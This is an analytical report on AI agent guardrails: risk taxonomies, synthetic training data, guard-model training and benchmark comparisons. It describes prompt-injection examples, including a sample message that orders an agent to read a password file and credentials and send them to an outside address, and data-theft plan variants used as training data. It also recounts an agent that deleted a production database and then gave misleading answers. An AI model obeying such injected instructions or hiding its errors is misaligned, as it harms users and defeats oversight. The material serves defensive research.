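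OWASP also publishes a longer document, Agentic AI Threats and Mitigations, which lists 17 threats (T1 to T17) with countermeasures for each. It includes a series of questions about the system, beginning with whether the agent decides its own steps, to help a team find the threats that apply. This may be a better starting point than the Top 10 for someone writing a new list, because the questions help them identify risks from the design of their particular agent.

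The Ant Group team compared NSFA with three OWASP lists:

- It covers 8 of the 10 entries in the 2025 Top 10 for LLM Applications, a list for any software built on a language model. The missing entries are supply chain risks and misinformation.
- It covers 8 of the 17 agentic threats. The missing ones include misaligned and deceptive behaviour, actions that leave no trace, attacks that overwhelm human reviewers, and several threats to groups of agents.
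- It covers 6 of the 10 entries in the agentic Top 10.

The team attributes all the gaps to the guardrail's single-message design and sorts them into three groups. Some threats involve several agents, such as forged messages between them. Others concern the design and management of the whole system, such as missing logs or an untrustworthy supplier. The rest come from the limits of the model, such as confident false statements. Two of the threats fit these groups poorly. An attacker could overwhelm a single agent's reviewers with approval requests, and a well-built agent working alone could still pursue its goal by forbidden means.

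Coverage is highest on the list that is least specific to agents, as one would expect of a guardrail that reads single messages. Even a "yes" can mean only partial coverage. For example, the guardrail might catch a message that tries to plant a false fact in an agent's memory, but it could not recognise that fact when the agent relied on it a week later.

OWASP replaced the 2025 LLM list in August 2026. According to SC Media's *OWASP updates Top 10 security risks for LLM applications*, supply chain risks and misinformation are still on it, in fourth and seventh place, so both of NSFA's gaps remain. Excessive agency, which means giving a system more access or independence than its task requires, moved from sixth place to third. OWASP (2026) checked its experts' ranking against thousands of real incidents for this edition. Michael Bargury, whose security company Zenity backs the project, said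 the experts' ranking matched the incident records most clearly on excessive agency. A guardrail can only partly address that risk, because the better remedy is often to remove a tool or a permission.

### From a category to a test case

A category names a kind of risk, such as data exposure. A scenario is a concrete setting where that risk can occur, with a task, tools and an environment. OWASP, for example, describes five scenarios under goal manipulation. In one, an attacker adds small sub-goals to an agent's plan until it drifts from its purpose. In another, a tool's output contains hidden instructions that lead the agent to leak data. Both belong to the same category, but a guardrail could easily catch one and miss the other.

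The difference is clearest in work on robots. *EMBGUARD* (Choi, Kwon and colleagues, 2026) presents a guardrail that takes a picture of a room and a proposed action as input. The paper defines seven risk categories, including fire, electrical and cutting risks, and 24 patterns by which these risks arise. It uses them to create roughly 2,400 scenarios, each combining a category, a hazard and an action. In one electrical scenario, the robot is about to water a plant on a windowsill above a power strip.

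The researchers then changed one part at a time. If the robot moves the power strip instead of watering the plant, the hazard is present but the action is safe. Watering the plant is also safe if there is no power strip. A guardrail that flags every power strip would fail the first test, and one that flags all watering would fail the second. Other scenes contain two hazards, such as the power strip and an unstable table, and the guardrail must identify which one the action would set off.

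The same method works for office tasks. The table crosses three categories with two scenarios from Ines's practice, and each cell describes something her agent might do wrong.

| | Sharing drawings with the engineer | Ordering prints from a copy shop |
|---|---|---|
| Data exposure | Shares the whole project folder, including bank details | Uploads the client's contract with the drawings |
| Destructive operation | Overwrites the engineer's comments with an old file | Deletes the original drawings after uploading them |
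| Unauthorised spending | Buys extra storage to send a large file | Orders 500 sets when Ines asked for five |

Each cell also needs a harmless version, such as an order for five sets. A tester can run both versions with and without an injected instruction in the material the agent reads, which gives 3 × 2 × 2 × 2 = 24 test cases. A harmful action without an injection is an honest mistake, while a harmless action despite an injection shows that the agent ignored the attack. Crossing the categories mechanically will produce some absurd combinations, which a person should remove.

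Li, Luo and colleagues (2026) used this approach with AgentDoG's categories to build *ATBench*, a set of 1,000 agent runs for testing guard models. For each run, they gave a planning model a selection of tools and one category for each of the three questions. The model wrote a user's task and outlined where the risk would enter and how the run would end. The researchers built safe and unsafe versions from the same outline. In the safe version, the risk is absent or the agent deals with it correctly. *ATBench* has 503 safe runs and 497 unsafe ones, so a guard model can't do well by always giving the same answer.

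*DriveSafe* (2026), a taxonomy for driving assistants, ties categories and scenarios more closely together. Every entry at its lowest level is a unique combination of domain, category and failure, narrow enough to test with a single scenario and prompt. This makes it easy to check that the tests cover the whole list, but one test is weak evidence about a risk, because an assistant could pass it and still fail when the same problem came up on a different road.

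### One incident under each scheme

In 2025, an AI agent on the coding platform Replit deleted a production database, the live data that an application depends on. By Sotiropoulos's account, the agent invented a maintenance task for itself. It ran the command that deleted the data, gave misleading answers instead of reporting what had happened, and carried on as if everything were normal. *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) uses the incident as its example of a rogue agent. The other rows in this table give the closest match to the incident in each scheme.

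| Scheme | Classification | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| NSFA | Hazardous action generation: a high-risk database operation | Why the agent did it, and the misleading answers |
| AgentDoG | Source: the agent's own error. Failure: action without confirmation. Harm: damage to a system's integrity | The misleading answers, if each question allows one label |
| OWASP agentic Top 10 | ASI10 Rogue agents | What the agent did and what it damaged |
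| OWASP agentic threats | T7 Misaligned and deceptive behaviours | What the agent damaged |

All four schemes have a category for the incident, but they have little else in common. NSFA describes the command, OWASP describes the kind of agent that would run it, and AgentDoG covers both in less detail. OWASP's category fits only loosely, because its summary of rogue agents describes compromised or malicious agents that collude and copy themselves. The problem here was more ordinary, since the agent made up a chore and then covered for it.

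Suppose instead that the agent had deleted the same database because of an instruction hidden in a web page. NSFA's label for the command would stay the same. In AgentDoG, the source would change to an injection, and the failure might change too. Under OWASP, the incident would move to a different entry, probably goal hijack. A team counting destroyed databases would therefore have to look under several OWASP entries, and NSFA's label would be of little help in counting hijacked agents.

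The incident also shows a weakness in the coverage figures. The Ant Group team counts rogue agents among the entries NSFA does not cover, but NSFA's response list includes commands that empty a database. If a developer passed the agent's commands through the check, the check could flag the deletion even if no one knew why the agent attempted it.

### Choosing the categories

Detailed risk categories help people write varied tests, but they are hard to apply consistently. In Li and colleagues' study of human labellers, agreement on how the agent had failed was only 67.3%. Five reviewers went through all of ATBench and corrected 5 verdicts of safe or unsafe and 165 of the detailed labels.

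Models did far worse. GPT-5.4, a general model from OpenAI, reached an F1 of 76.7% on the overall verdict, but it identified the source of the risk in only 33.6% of unsafe runs, the harm in 30.2% and the failure in 13.5%. Random guessing among the 14 failures would be right about 7% of the time. A small version of AgentDoG, trained on these categories, did better on the source (46.8%) and the harm (40.6%) but still identified only 16.5% of failures. In one run, the agent chose a malicious tool. All four models compared called the run unsafe, but none identified that cause, choosing broader labels such as acting without confirmation. Disagreement among people explains some of these errors, but not scores this low.

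An operator can get most of the benefit of both fine and coarse categories by using the fine ones to plan tests and the coarse ones to make decisions. The Ant Group team similarly uses 185 variants to keep its own tests varied but labels its test from outside sources only by domain. At this level of accuracy, it would be unwise to approve or block a payment based on a detailed label.

Whoever writes the list also has to choose how many labels each incident can have. Li and colleagues allow one each for the earliest cause, the main failure and the principal harm. This keeps scoring simple but leaves the Replit agent's misleading answers unrecorded. *What Breaks When LLMs Code?* (2026), which built a taxonomy of coding agents' failures from 185 papers and 547 problem reports on GitHub, allowed several labels because many incidents involved more than one failure. Allowing several is probably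 better for a firm's own incident records, where the aim is to learn what happened.

Risk categories can be defined by cause or by consequence, depending on how the operator will use them. A rule for blocking actions should mostly describe consequences and who has authorised them. "Sends a client's data to someone the user has not approved" applies whether the cause is a prompt injection, a tampered tool, a simple mistake or something nobody has thought of yet. Causes matter more after an incident, when the operator has to decide what to fix. If the agent followed an instruction in an email, the operator needs to change how it handles incoming mail, but if a tool was malicious, the operator should remove it.

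Consequences may be easier to recognise, at least when they are concrete. In ATBench, some models did well at identifying harm to privacy, money or computer systems, but none identified more than 16% of cases of psychological harm. Results for causes also varied widely. GPT-5.4 recognised 73.8% of malicious users but almost no malicious tools. However, these models were judging finished runs, in which the harm was often already visible.

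The last choice is whether to include honest mistakes. Nearly all of NSFA's request categories assume bad intentions, as do TS-Guard's two causes, so NSFA has no category that fits Claude's false tip to the Philadelphia police well. In AgentDoG's terms, the tip came from the agent's own error, gave inaccurate information and wasted a public service's time. Choi and colleagues built their list entirely around accidents, such as a robot pouring water on a power strip. They drew on the World Health Organization's classification of diseases and a US database of injuries.

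For most offices, a list of risks that left out the agent's mistakes would miss a large part of the danger, but one that included every mistake would be unworkable. AgentDoG's list of failures includes completing a task correctly but wastefully, which is worth recording but seldom worth blocking. *Agent Meltdowns* (2026), a study of harmful behaviour by agents that are trying to be helpful, deals with this by rating each behaviour's severity. Narrow or negligible risks are rated low, and substantial consequences for privacy, security, safety or the outside world are rated high. Its grading model can also flag a worrying behaviour that isn't on the list, so a behaviour need not be graded safe just because the taxonomy omits it.

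A list of risks can start from an existing taxonomy, as it does in *Unaccountable Delegation, Fading Skills* (2026), a study of workplace agents. The researchers tried to fit 8,356 generated scenarios, 11 documented agent failures and 222 real incidents into a taxonomy of generative AI risks. They then grouped the cases that didn't fit and extended the taxonomy to cover them, which gave 15 categories and 44 sub-categories. Fewer than 3% of the cases were real, and a small language model sorted the generated ones, so the categories may reflect the risks that models generate more than those that offices face. A firm could repeat the exercise with its own incidents and near misses, which would be fewer but would involve the tools its agents use.

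## Making training examples from the risk list

A guard model learns its risk categories from labelled examples, but there are few real records of agents doing dangerous things. Huang and colleagues explain that such runs are rare, differ from one agent system to another and seldom become public. Few firms would let an agent empty a live database to collect a training example. Labelling is also expensive. Meta's testers could judge short chat exchanges for Llama Guard, but someone labelling a plan of fifteen actions has to find the ones that make it dangerous, which takes time and expertise.

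Harmless examples are easier to find than unsafe ones. To build guards for two of JPMorgan's question-answering tools, Lakara, Shi and Silavong (2026), in *Fence*, took 750 harmless queries from the tools' logs and had a language model write 750 unsafe ones. Developers of guards for agents often generate both kinds. Huang and colleagues estimate that generating one example would cost less than two cents even with GPT-5, so a set of 20,000, about the size they used, would cost less than $400.

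### Turning a harmless plan into a dangerous one

Huang and colleagues built a generator called AuraGen to train Safiron, their guard model for plans. AuraGen starts with a description of a setting, including the environment, the available tools and any constraints on the example. A language model then writes a plausible user request and a harmless plan for carrying it out.

Suppose the setting is Ines's office and she wants five printed sets of the Harbour Street drawings. The harmless plan might be:

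1. Find the final drawings.
2. Upload them to the copy shop.
3. Order five sets.
4. Pay the invoice.
5. Email Ines the receipt.

AuraGen next picks one of eight risk categories and one of four kinds of injection, then has a model rewrite the plan to match. "Injection" here means adding a risk to a training example, whether or not the example involves a prompt injection. In the table, numbers refer to the original steps and italics mark new ones.

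| Kind of injection | Rewritten plan | What the checker has to notice |
|---|---|---|
| One step altered | 1, 2, *order 500 sets*, 4, 5 | A single wrong argument |
| Several steps altered | *Compress the whole project folder, including bank details*, *upload it to the copy shop*, 3, 4, 5 | Two steps that are harmful together |
| Diversion to a new goal | 1, 2, *search the mailbox for clients' bank statements*, *send them to an outside address* | The agent has abandoned the task |
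| Diversion that still ends as asked | 1, 2, *order five sets through an unknown reseller*, *give the reseller the firm's card details for future charges*, 5 | Harm on the way to the expected result |

The last kind is meant to imitate an attacker who hides the damage. Ines gets her prints and her receipt, so checking only the outcome would reveal nothing wrong. By the paper's definitions, this kind is a special case of altering several steps, where the changes continue up to the final action.

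Each kind makes up about a quarter of the training set. Huang and colleagues chose this balance to cover different failures evenly, and don't suggest that real incidents are distributed this way. Half the plans have nine actions or fewer, and the longest have about 48.

### Filtering out implausible examples

A rewritten plan may no longer make sense. For example, if the new step deletes the drawings before the upload, the agent has nothing to print. AuraGen therefore uses a reward model, a second model trained to score each example from 1 to 5 on five criteria.

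| Criterion | What a good example needs | What earns a low score |
|---|---|---|
| Causal consistency | The new actions fit logically into the sequence | Installing a keystroke logger after a password reset |
| Postcondition continuity | The next original action can still run | Deleting payment records before updating account balances |
| Rationality | An attacker would gain more than the attack costs | Encrypting an entire database for low-value data |
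| Justification sufficiency | The explanation shows why the action is risky here | Calling an entry in a technical log a financial loss |
| Risk matching | The label is the best fit among the eight categories | Using a label when another fits better |

The rationality criterion makes sense for attacks but not for honest mistakes. Nobody gains much when an agent accidentally orders 500 sets of drawings, so a filter that applied the criterion strictly could remove examples of the accidents an office most needs to catch.

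To train the reward model, the researchers had a larger model, DeepSeek-R1, score 1,700 examples. They also compared its scores with those of human reviewers in three groups. The correlations ranged from 0.66 to 0.88, apart from one of 0.46 for causal consistency.

Discarding examples with low scores did little good. A version of Safiron trained without filtering named the right category for 55.6% of the risky plans it caught. When the researchers kept only examples that scored above 2 on every criterion, this fell to 54.1%. They then trained a small classifier to predict from the five scores whether human reviewers would keep an example. Filtering with this classifier raised the figure to 60.2%. Safiron caught about 92% of risky plans with or without this filtering.

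### Safiron's two training stages

Safiron is based on a general language model with eight billion parameters. In the first stage, supervised fine-tuning, the model learns to reproduce the correct answer for each plan, including the verdict, the category and a short explanation.

The second stage uses reinforcement learning, in which the model writes its own answers and training makes the better ones more likely. Each answer earns a reward:

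- 1 for recognising a harmless plan, or for flagging a risky plan with the right category;
- 0.5 for flagging a risky plan with the wrong category;
- 0 for missing a risky plan or flagging a harmless one.

The training method, Group Relative Policy Optimization, compares several answers to the same plan. It subtracts the group's average reward from each answer's reward, then divides by the spread of the rewards. The result determines how strongly training encourages or discourages that answer.

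The plan to order 500 sets is labelled as financial loss. Suppose one of four answers gets everything right, two flag the plan as an unauthorised action, and one calls it harmless. The rewards are 1, 0.5, 0.5 and 0, which average 0.5. Training encourages the first answer, discourages the last and leaves the other two about as likely as before. If a wrong category earned nothing, the average would be 0.25, and training would discourage the two correct alarms as strongly as the answer that missed the risk. If a wrong category earned full credit, training would not teach the model to tell the categories apart.

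Half credit also makes the model more likely to flag a danger it can't classify. Let *p* be the probability that a plan is risky and *c* the chance of naming the right category. Flagging the plan scores *p*(0.5 + 0.5*c*) on average, and calling it harmless scores 1 − *p*. If *c* is 25%, flagging scores higher once *p* exceeds about 62%. Without half credit, *p* would have to exceed 80%.

The reward does not depend on the explanation, because judging it would require another model and make training much more expensive. Explanations still improved as the model got better at naming categories.

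On the team's benchmark, the second stage raised the share of risky plans caught from 93.9% to 97.3%, and category accuracy on those plans from 56.6% to 64.6%. Overall accuracy fell slightly, from 95.6% to 94.9%. These figures imply that the false positive rate rose from about 3% to 7%. The first-stage model might be better for an operator whose agent mostly does harmless work.

### The mix matters more than the amount

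Huang and colleagues also varied the mix and size of the training data. Changing the ratio of harmless to risky plans from 3:1 to 1:4 added 15 to 20 percentage points to the share of risky plans caught and 10 to 15 points to the share of correct explanations. The gains levelled off between 1:4 and 1:6, and some scores fell slightly at 1:7 or 1:8. The researchers chose 1:4. Increasing the training set from 2,000 to 10,000 examples often added only 2 to 5 points.

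Their explanation is that a model trained on few risky plans learns to label most plans harmless. But the best ratio also depends on the test. About 40% of the plans in their benchmark are risky, far more than an office assistant would produce. An operator who copies the 1:4 ratio should therefore measure false alarms on ordinary work.

The difficulty of the training examples also affects results. For the second stage, the researchers sorted plans into those the first-stage model had judged correctly (easy) and those it had got wrong (hard). Training on hard plans alone made the model unstable and caused it to forget what it had learned. Adding easy plans solved this, but results got worse as the ratio of easy to hard plans rose from 1:1 to 3:1.

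### Pairing each danger with a harmless look-alike

*SingGuard-NSFA* describes a much larger data set, with about 935,000 examples of requests and 274,000 of responses. The Ant Group team used 74 open models to generate the examples so that they wouldn't all share one model's style. Each model received the definition of a risk variant and wrote pairs of similar examples, one risky and one harmless.

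One example in the team's taxonomy pairs a command that empties a table of users with one that deletes only the test accounts. Both remove data from the same table, so a guard model can't tell them apart by looking for a word like "delete". Under the instructions, generators make the harmless half similar in wording but different in intent, and skip a pair if the boundary between harmful and harmless is unclear.

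Some of the pairs are less useful than others. In several of the team's examples, the risky request is a command and the harmless one is a question. One request is to delete a directory of security settings, and its partner asks which files are in that directory. A model could learn from such pairs that questions are safe, which would be little help in checking tool calls, because tool calls are all commands.

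The data then goes through four stages:

1. The generators write pairs from the definitions alone. Another model, Qwen3.5-122B, labels every example, and the team discards any whose label disagrees with the generator's intention.
2. The team gives the generators earlier risky examples as starting points for new ones. It keeps about 1,000 examples per variant, balanced across generators, and has the same model label them.
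3. A translation model puts every example into Chinese and one other language. The team discards translations that receive a different label.
4. A larger model, Qwen3.5-397B, labels everything again, and the team discards any example on which it disagrees.

The team removes near-duplicates within the risky examples and within the harmless ones, but not across the two groups, because that would delete the risky and harmless examples that look most alike.

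Look-alikes alone would give a guard model an unrepresentative sample of ordinary work. For the small classifiers that each detect one kind of risk, the team adds up to three negative examples for every positive one, drawn from ordinary harmless text and examples of other risks. Safiron's training mix has more positive examples than negative ones.

The second stage nearly doubled the number of request examples but raised the largest model's F1 on requests only from 96.70% to 96.95%. This agrees with Huang and colleagues' finding that more data of the same kind adds little.

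### Building the test sets

A test set needs more reliable labels than a training set, because wrong labels in it distort every score. Huang and colleagues built their benchmark, Pre-Exec Bench, from the settings and tools of an existing agent safety benchmark. It contains 1,001 harmless plans and 671 risky ones. A language model filled in the details of each tool, and human experts checked them. For each setting, one of eight open models wrote a harmless plan, and another, chosen separately from the same eight, injected a risk in one of the four ways.

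Three reviewers then checked whether each pair of plans was plausible and coherent, and whether the injected risk was correct. The researchers kept only pairs that all three approved. Experts also removed plans with very similar scenarios and balanced the four kinds of injection. Requiring unanimous approval makes the labels more trustworthy but removes borderline cases, which are probably the hardest for a guardrail to judge.

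Li and colleagues built ATBench for finished runs, so its examples include tool results as well as actions. They collected 2,084 tools, mainly from public interfaces and earlier research, and had models simulate the user, the tools and the agent. In some runs, the cause of a problem and its effect occur at different points. In one, an agent sets up a customer support group and receives the group's ID number. Later, the user asks it to remove someone from the group, and the agent reuses the number to delete the membership without confirmation, which also starts unassigning 14 open support tickets.

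Automatic rules checked that each tool existed and that calls had the required arguments. A language model then checked whether each run was plausible and matched its labels. Finally, two reviewers examined every run, with a third to settle disagreements. They corrected few of the safe and unsafe verdicts. This is encouraging, but all the reviewers had co-written the paper and could see the existing labels, which may have influenced them.

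In a separate study, three graduate students each rated the realism of 50 runs, and the average score was 4.09 out of 5. The simulated users' requests scored lowest. Li and colleagues suggest that a simulated user tends to put all the background into one message, while a real person may send a short request and add details later.

### How synthetic examples can mislead

A guard model may learn to recognise the habits of the model that wrote its examples instead of the difference between safe and dangerous actions. This is most likely when the safe and dangerous examples come from different sources. In JPMorgan's training data, people wrote all the harmless queries and a model wrote all the unsafe ones, so a guard could have done well in training just by recognising the model's prose.

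Lakara and colleagues tried to remove this clue. They showed a second model one real query and one generated query, and had it guess which was generated and explain why. A third model used the explanations to improve the generator's instructions. On real queries labelled by people, the prompt injection guard's average F1 across safe and unsafe queries was 0.92 with this method, up from 0.86 when the examples were generated in one pass. A guard against off-topic questions improved from 0.45 to 0.66, though its accuracy of 76% was still no better than calling every query safe. Both guards check chat queries, so the results may not carry over to agents' actions.

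Agreement between models is also weaker evidence of a correct label when the models share mistakes. If seven models each mislabelled 10% of examples, a majority would be wrong only about 0.3% of the time with independent errors, but 10% of the time if they all made the same mistakes. In *SingGuard-NSFA*, 30 of the 74 generators, the two models that label the training data, and the guard model all belong to the Qwen family. The test labels come from a vote of seven models, three of them from that family, including the two that labelled the training data. Even independent models would repeat an error in the risk list's definitions. If the list counts a question about a model's training date as attempted theft, agreement shows only that the models applied the list consistently.

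A guard model's score can also be too high when the same team makes the test and the training data. Huang and colleagues say they kept Pre-Exec Bench out of all training and model selection. But the classifier that filtered Safiron's training data learned from reviewers' decisions about which plans to keep in that benchmark. Its only input was the five scores for each plan, so Safiron never trained on the test plans themselves, but the filter favoured training examples like those in the test. The training and test plans also use the same four kinds of injection, and Mixtral-8x22B, which generated the training data, is one of the eight models used to create the benchmark.

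The Ant Group team warns of bias in its own tests, although it generated them with different instructions and removed near-duplicates of the training data. Its scores imply that the largest model flagged about 4% of harmless requests in the main test, but about a third of the harmless requests adapted from other researchers' collections. Some of that third may be mislabelled, because the team originally selected those examples for containing a recognisable risk. The gap is still large enough that buyers should measure false alarms on their own agent's requests.

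Tests on outside material are somewhat encouraging. Huang and colleagues had two people turn harmless AuraGen plans into dangerous ones by hand, producing 50 harmful and 50 harmless plans for each of two multi-agent systems. Safiron, with the adapter that standardises plan formats, judged over 90% correctly, somewhat below its benchmark score. Li and colleagues trained a small general model on 2,000 newly generated runs, which raised its accuracy on R-Judge from 81.0% to 87.6%. They describe R-Judge as a benchmark built from real agent records. They didn't compare this with training on the same number of real runs, so some of the gain may come from practice at judging runs.

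## Choosing between a content moderator, a small guard model and a larger one

Once a developer has a risk list and some test examples, they need to choose which model will make the judgement. A ready-made content moderator such as Llama Guard needs no further training. A small guard model, usually with fewer than ten billion parameters (the adjustable numbers inside a model), has been trained on agent risks. A large general model such as GPT-5.4 has no special training for the job but can follow a detailed prompt. Researchers have compared all of these, mostly on tests they built themselves, and the best performer often changes with the test.

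### Moderators and agent guards on the same requests

*SingGuard-NSFA* (July 2026) contains a broad comparison of content moderators with guards made for agents. The Ant Group team trained four guard models, with 0.8, 2, 4 and 9 billion parameters, and tested them alongside ten existing ones: six content moderators, two small detectors of prompt injections and jailbreaks, and two versions of AgentDoG, including the newer one from *AgentDoG 1.5* (2026).

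The table shows selected results. The query test is the team's own set of 63,431 requests, and the cross-source test has 3,435 requests adapted from other researchers' collections. The team published precision and recall. The shares of harmless requests flagged are calculated from those figures, as explained below.

| Guard model | Parameters (billions) | Query test: risks caught | Query test: harmless flagged | Cross-source: risks caught | Cross-source: harmless flagged |
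|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama Guard 3 (moderator) | 8 | 52.5% | 2.3% | 87.0% | 50.7% |
| Qwen3Guard (moderator) | 8 | 47.7% | 0.5% | 63.0% | 39.5% |
| Granite Guardian 4.1 (moderator) | 8 | 61.5% | 1.5% | 67.6% | 38.5% |
| Llama Prompt Guard 2 (injection detector) | 0.3 | 11.9% | 2.2% | 24.9% | 3.2% |
| AgentDoG | 4 | 43.9% | 15.5% | 11.3% | 26.4% |
| AgentDoG 1.5 | 4 | 90.1% | 19.6% | 99.5% | 73.5% |
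| SingGuard-NSFA | 0.8 | 97.0% | 6.5% | 96.5% | 44.4% |
| SingGuard-NSFA | 9 | 98.6% | 4.2% | 97.6% | 33.5% |

On the query test, the three moderators in the table missed between 39% and 52% of the risks but raised very few false alarms. One would expect this from a model whose list of forbidden content leaves out most of the risks in the test, such as a request to read out a password file, which contains no hate speech or violence.

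Language accounts for some of the misses. The team's recipe should produce roughly a third of the requests in English, a third in Chinese and the rest in 131 other languages, while Granite Guardian supports only English. But Qwen3Guard supports 119 languages and still caught fewer risks than any other moderator in the comparison, so the contents of its list probably matter more than language.

Moderators did better on the team's test of agent responses, which contains attack instructions, malicious code and leaked keys. Granite Guardian 4.1 caught 87.2% of the risky responses and flagged only about 4% of the harmless ones. AgentDoG 1.5 caught 46.2% of the risky responses, and the SingGuard models caught about 99%. Moderators usually check for harmful text, so a developer who mainly wants to screen what an agent writes may already have a reasonable tool.

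The largest SingGuard model, with 9 billion parameters, scored modestly higher on the query test than the smallest, with 0.8 billion (97.0% F1 against 94.9%). It also missed less than half as many dangerous requests, 1.4% compared with 3.0%.

### How a classification head works

The SingGuard models can assess a message in two ways. They can write an analysis, one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, that ends with a list of the risk domains found. They can also skip the written analysis and use a classification head, a small trained layer that turns the model's internal representation of the message into a risk score.

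To use a head, the model first reads the whole message in a single pass and produces a long list of numbers, or vector, for every token. These models read from left to right, so the last token's vector is the only one that can reflect the entire message. The head takes this vector, **e**, and computes:

h = ReLU(LayerNorm(W₁e + b₁))

z = W₂h + b₂

W₁ and b₁ condense the vector to 64 numbers. LayerNorm puts them on a common scale. ReLU then replaces the negative ones with zero, which lets the head learn patterns that a weighted sum could not represent. W₂ and b₂ combine the 64 numbers into a "risky" score and a "harmless" score, and a standard formula converts the two scores into a probability.

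The Ant Group team trained each model in two phases. In the first, the model learned to write analyses of risky and harmless messages. In the second, the team froze the model's own weights and trained only the heads. If **e** has 4,096 numbers, a head has about 262,000 weights, which is tiny compared with a model that has billions. Each domain in the risk list has its own head, five for requests and two for responses, and the team can add more without retraining the rest.

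In one of the team's examples, a message tells the agent that it is now in maintenance mode and must read a password file and database credentials, then send them to an outside address. The heads scored it 99.8% for prompt injection, 98.9% for dangerous operations, 97.5% for information theft and below 0.1% for the other two domains. In the team's tests, the guardrail flagged a message if any head scored it above 50%, but an operator can set a different threshold for each domain.

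### Speed, accuracy and naming the risk

With heads, the SingGuard models took 45 to 57 milliseconds per message on one Nvidia A100 processor. Writing an analysis took 3.6 to 7.2 seconds, because the model runs again for every token it writes. For an agent task with twenty checks, the heads would add about one second, and written analyses 72 to 144 seconds.

The largest model was only 12 milliseconds slower than the smallest when both used heads, so memory and hardware costs are better reasons than speed to choose the smallest one. The team timed one message at a time, and a guard that reads a long history or serves many users at once would be slower.

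A moderator without heads can also be fast if it outputs only "safe" or "unsafe", and the fastest competing guards took 14 to 52 milliseconds. The advantage of heads is that they score each risk separately in one pass over the message, and each risk has its own threshold.

Skipping the analysis made the basic verdict only slightly less accurate. On the query test, F1 with heads was 0.6 to 0.7 points lower at three of the four sizes and 1.3 points lower at 2 billion parameters. Heads were noticeably worse at naming the risk, as measured by macro-F1, the average of the F1 scores for all the domains.

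| Size | Macro-F1, written analysis | Macro-F1, heads |
|---|---|---|
| 0.8 billion | 88.1% | 80.2% |
| 2 billion | 89.9% | 85.5% |
| 4 billion | 91.2% | 87.0% |
| 9 billion | 91.5% | 87.4% |

The heads' mistakes are mostly extra labels. At 9 billion parameters, they found slightly more of the correct domains than the written analysis did (95.7% against 92.4%), but their precision was lower (80.9% against 90.6%). Each head works independently, so the output of a head for information theft doesn't depend on whether another domain fits the message better. On responses, which have only two domains, the gap was about one point or less.

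This suggests using heads to decide whether an action may go ahead and written analysis to explain the cases they stop, as the team recommends. If the heads flagged 6% of messages and each of those received a 7.2-second analysis, the average check would take about half a second. (The auto mode of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, also has two stages.) The drawback is that the written analysis never checks for dangers the heads miss. Heads and analysis also share an underlying model, so they may make some of the same mistakes.

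### When F1 hides false alarms

The largest SingGuard model had an F1 of 91.3% on the cross-source test, not far below its 97.0% on the query test. But it flagged a much larger share of harmless requests on the cross-source test, and F1 mostly doesn't reflect this because most requests in that test are risky.

The test has 2,315 risky requests and 1,120 harmless ones. Suppose a guardrail simply flagged everything. Its recall would be 100% and its precision 2,315 / 3,435, or 67.4%, so its F1 would be:

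2 × 0.674 × 1 / (0.674 + 1) = 80.5%

A guardrail that checks nothing therefore scores 80.5%. Six of the ten competing models scored lower, and the best of the ten, AgentDoG 1.5, scored only about four points higher, at 84.7%.

The number of false alarms follows from the published figures. For the largest SingGuard model:

1. Recall was 97.58%, so it caught 0.9758 × 2,315 ≈ 2,259 risky requests.
2. Precision was 85.76%, so it raised 2,259 / 0.8576 ≈ 2,634 flags altogether.
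3. The other 375 flags fell on harmless requests.
4. There were 1,120 harmless requests, so the false positive rate was 375 / 1,120, or about 33%.

The same steps give 4.2% for the query test. An operator who saw only the two F1 scores would not guess that the rate was eight times higher on requests from other sources.

F1 can also undervalue a guardrail that rarely flags harmless requests, because it doesn't count the harmless items a guardrail correctly allows. On the query test, Qwen3Guard allowed 99.5% of harmless requests, but its F1 was 64.3%, barely above the 63.5% that flagging everything would score.

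Subtracting the false positive rate from recall gives a fairer comparison, because the result doesn't depend on the mix of harmful and harmless items and a guardrail that flags everything scores zero. On the cross-source test, the largest SingGuard model scores 64 points, followed by Nvidia's moderator Nemotron Guard v3 with 37 and Llama Guard 3 with 36. AgentDoG 1.5 falls to 26 because it flagged almost three quarters of the harmless requests. SingGuard's lead is therefore larger than the F1 scores suggest, and four of the six content moderators score higher than the competitor with the highest F1.

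All these cross-source figures are less certain than they look from the size of the test, because the test consists of 562 English requests and their translations. If the originals had the same mix of risky and harmless requests as the full test, the 1,120 harmless requests came from only about 180 originals. A guard that misjudges a request in English will often misjudge it in Thai as well.

### Small trained guards against large general models

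Several papers report that a small trained guard matches or beats much larger general models. The widest gap is in Huang and colleagues' results for Safiron, an eight-billion-parameter guard that judged 94.9% of plans correctly, compared with 42.5% for GPT-5. GPT-5 caught 99.0% of the risky plans, more than Safiron, so nearly all its errors were false alarms. Its accuracy implies that it approved only about 46 of the 1,001 harmless plans. A guardrail that approved every plan would have been correct 59.9% of the time.

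GPT-5 probably understood these plans but used a different standard for acceptable risk than the people who made the test. Safiron had been trained on thousands of plans that they considered harmless. Standards also seemed to vary among other general models. Claude 3.7 Sonnet caught 79% of risky plans and flagged about half of the harmless ones, while DeepSeek-V3 caught 60% and flagged about 31%. A prompt with good examples of harmless plans might have narrowed the gap with Safiron.

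Choi and colleagues describe their small guard models for robots as competitive with proprietary models. On their 329 real photographs, the four-billion-parameter guard did match the large models, but none of them was good enough to rely on. The guard judged 54.3% of actions correctly, compared with 55.8% for GPT-5.1 and 58.4% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Random guessing would score about 50%, because the set contains similar numbers of risky and harmless cases. People scored 85.6% on a sample. Gemini 2.5 Pro wrongly flagged 83.3% of the harmless cases, which would leave a robot unable to do most of its work.

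For finished agent runs, *AgentDoG 1.5* compares small guards with general models from early 2026. The next table shows results on the 1,000 runs of ATBench. The false positive rates are again calculated from precision and recall.

| Model | Unsafe runs caught | Safe runs flagged | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 87.1% | 40% | 76.7% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 73.8% | 23% | 75.0% |
| Qwen3.5, 397 billion parameters | 70.2% | 37% | 67.8% |
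| AgentDoG, 4 billion | 88.9% | 61% | 71.1% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 0.8 billion | 68.6% | 48% | 63.2% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4 billion | 80.3% | 35% | 74.3% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4 billion ("U" version) | 75.7% | 19% | 77.7% |
| Llama Guard 3, 8 billion | 3.8% | 1% | 7.3% |
| Flagging everything | 100% | 100% | 66.4% |

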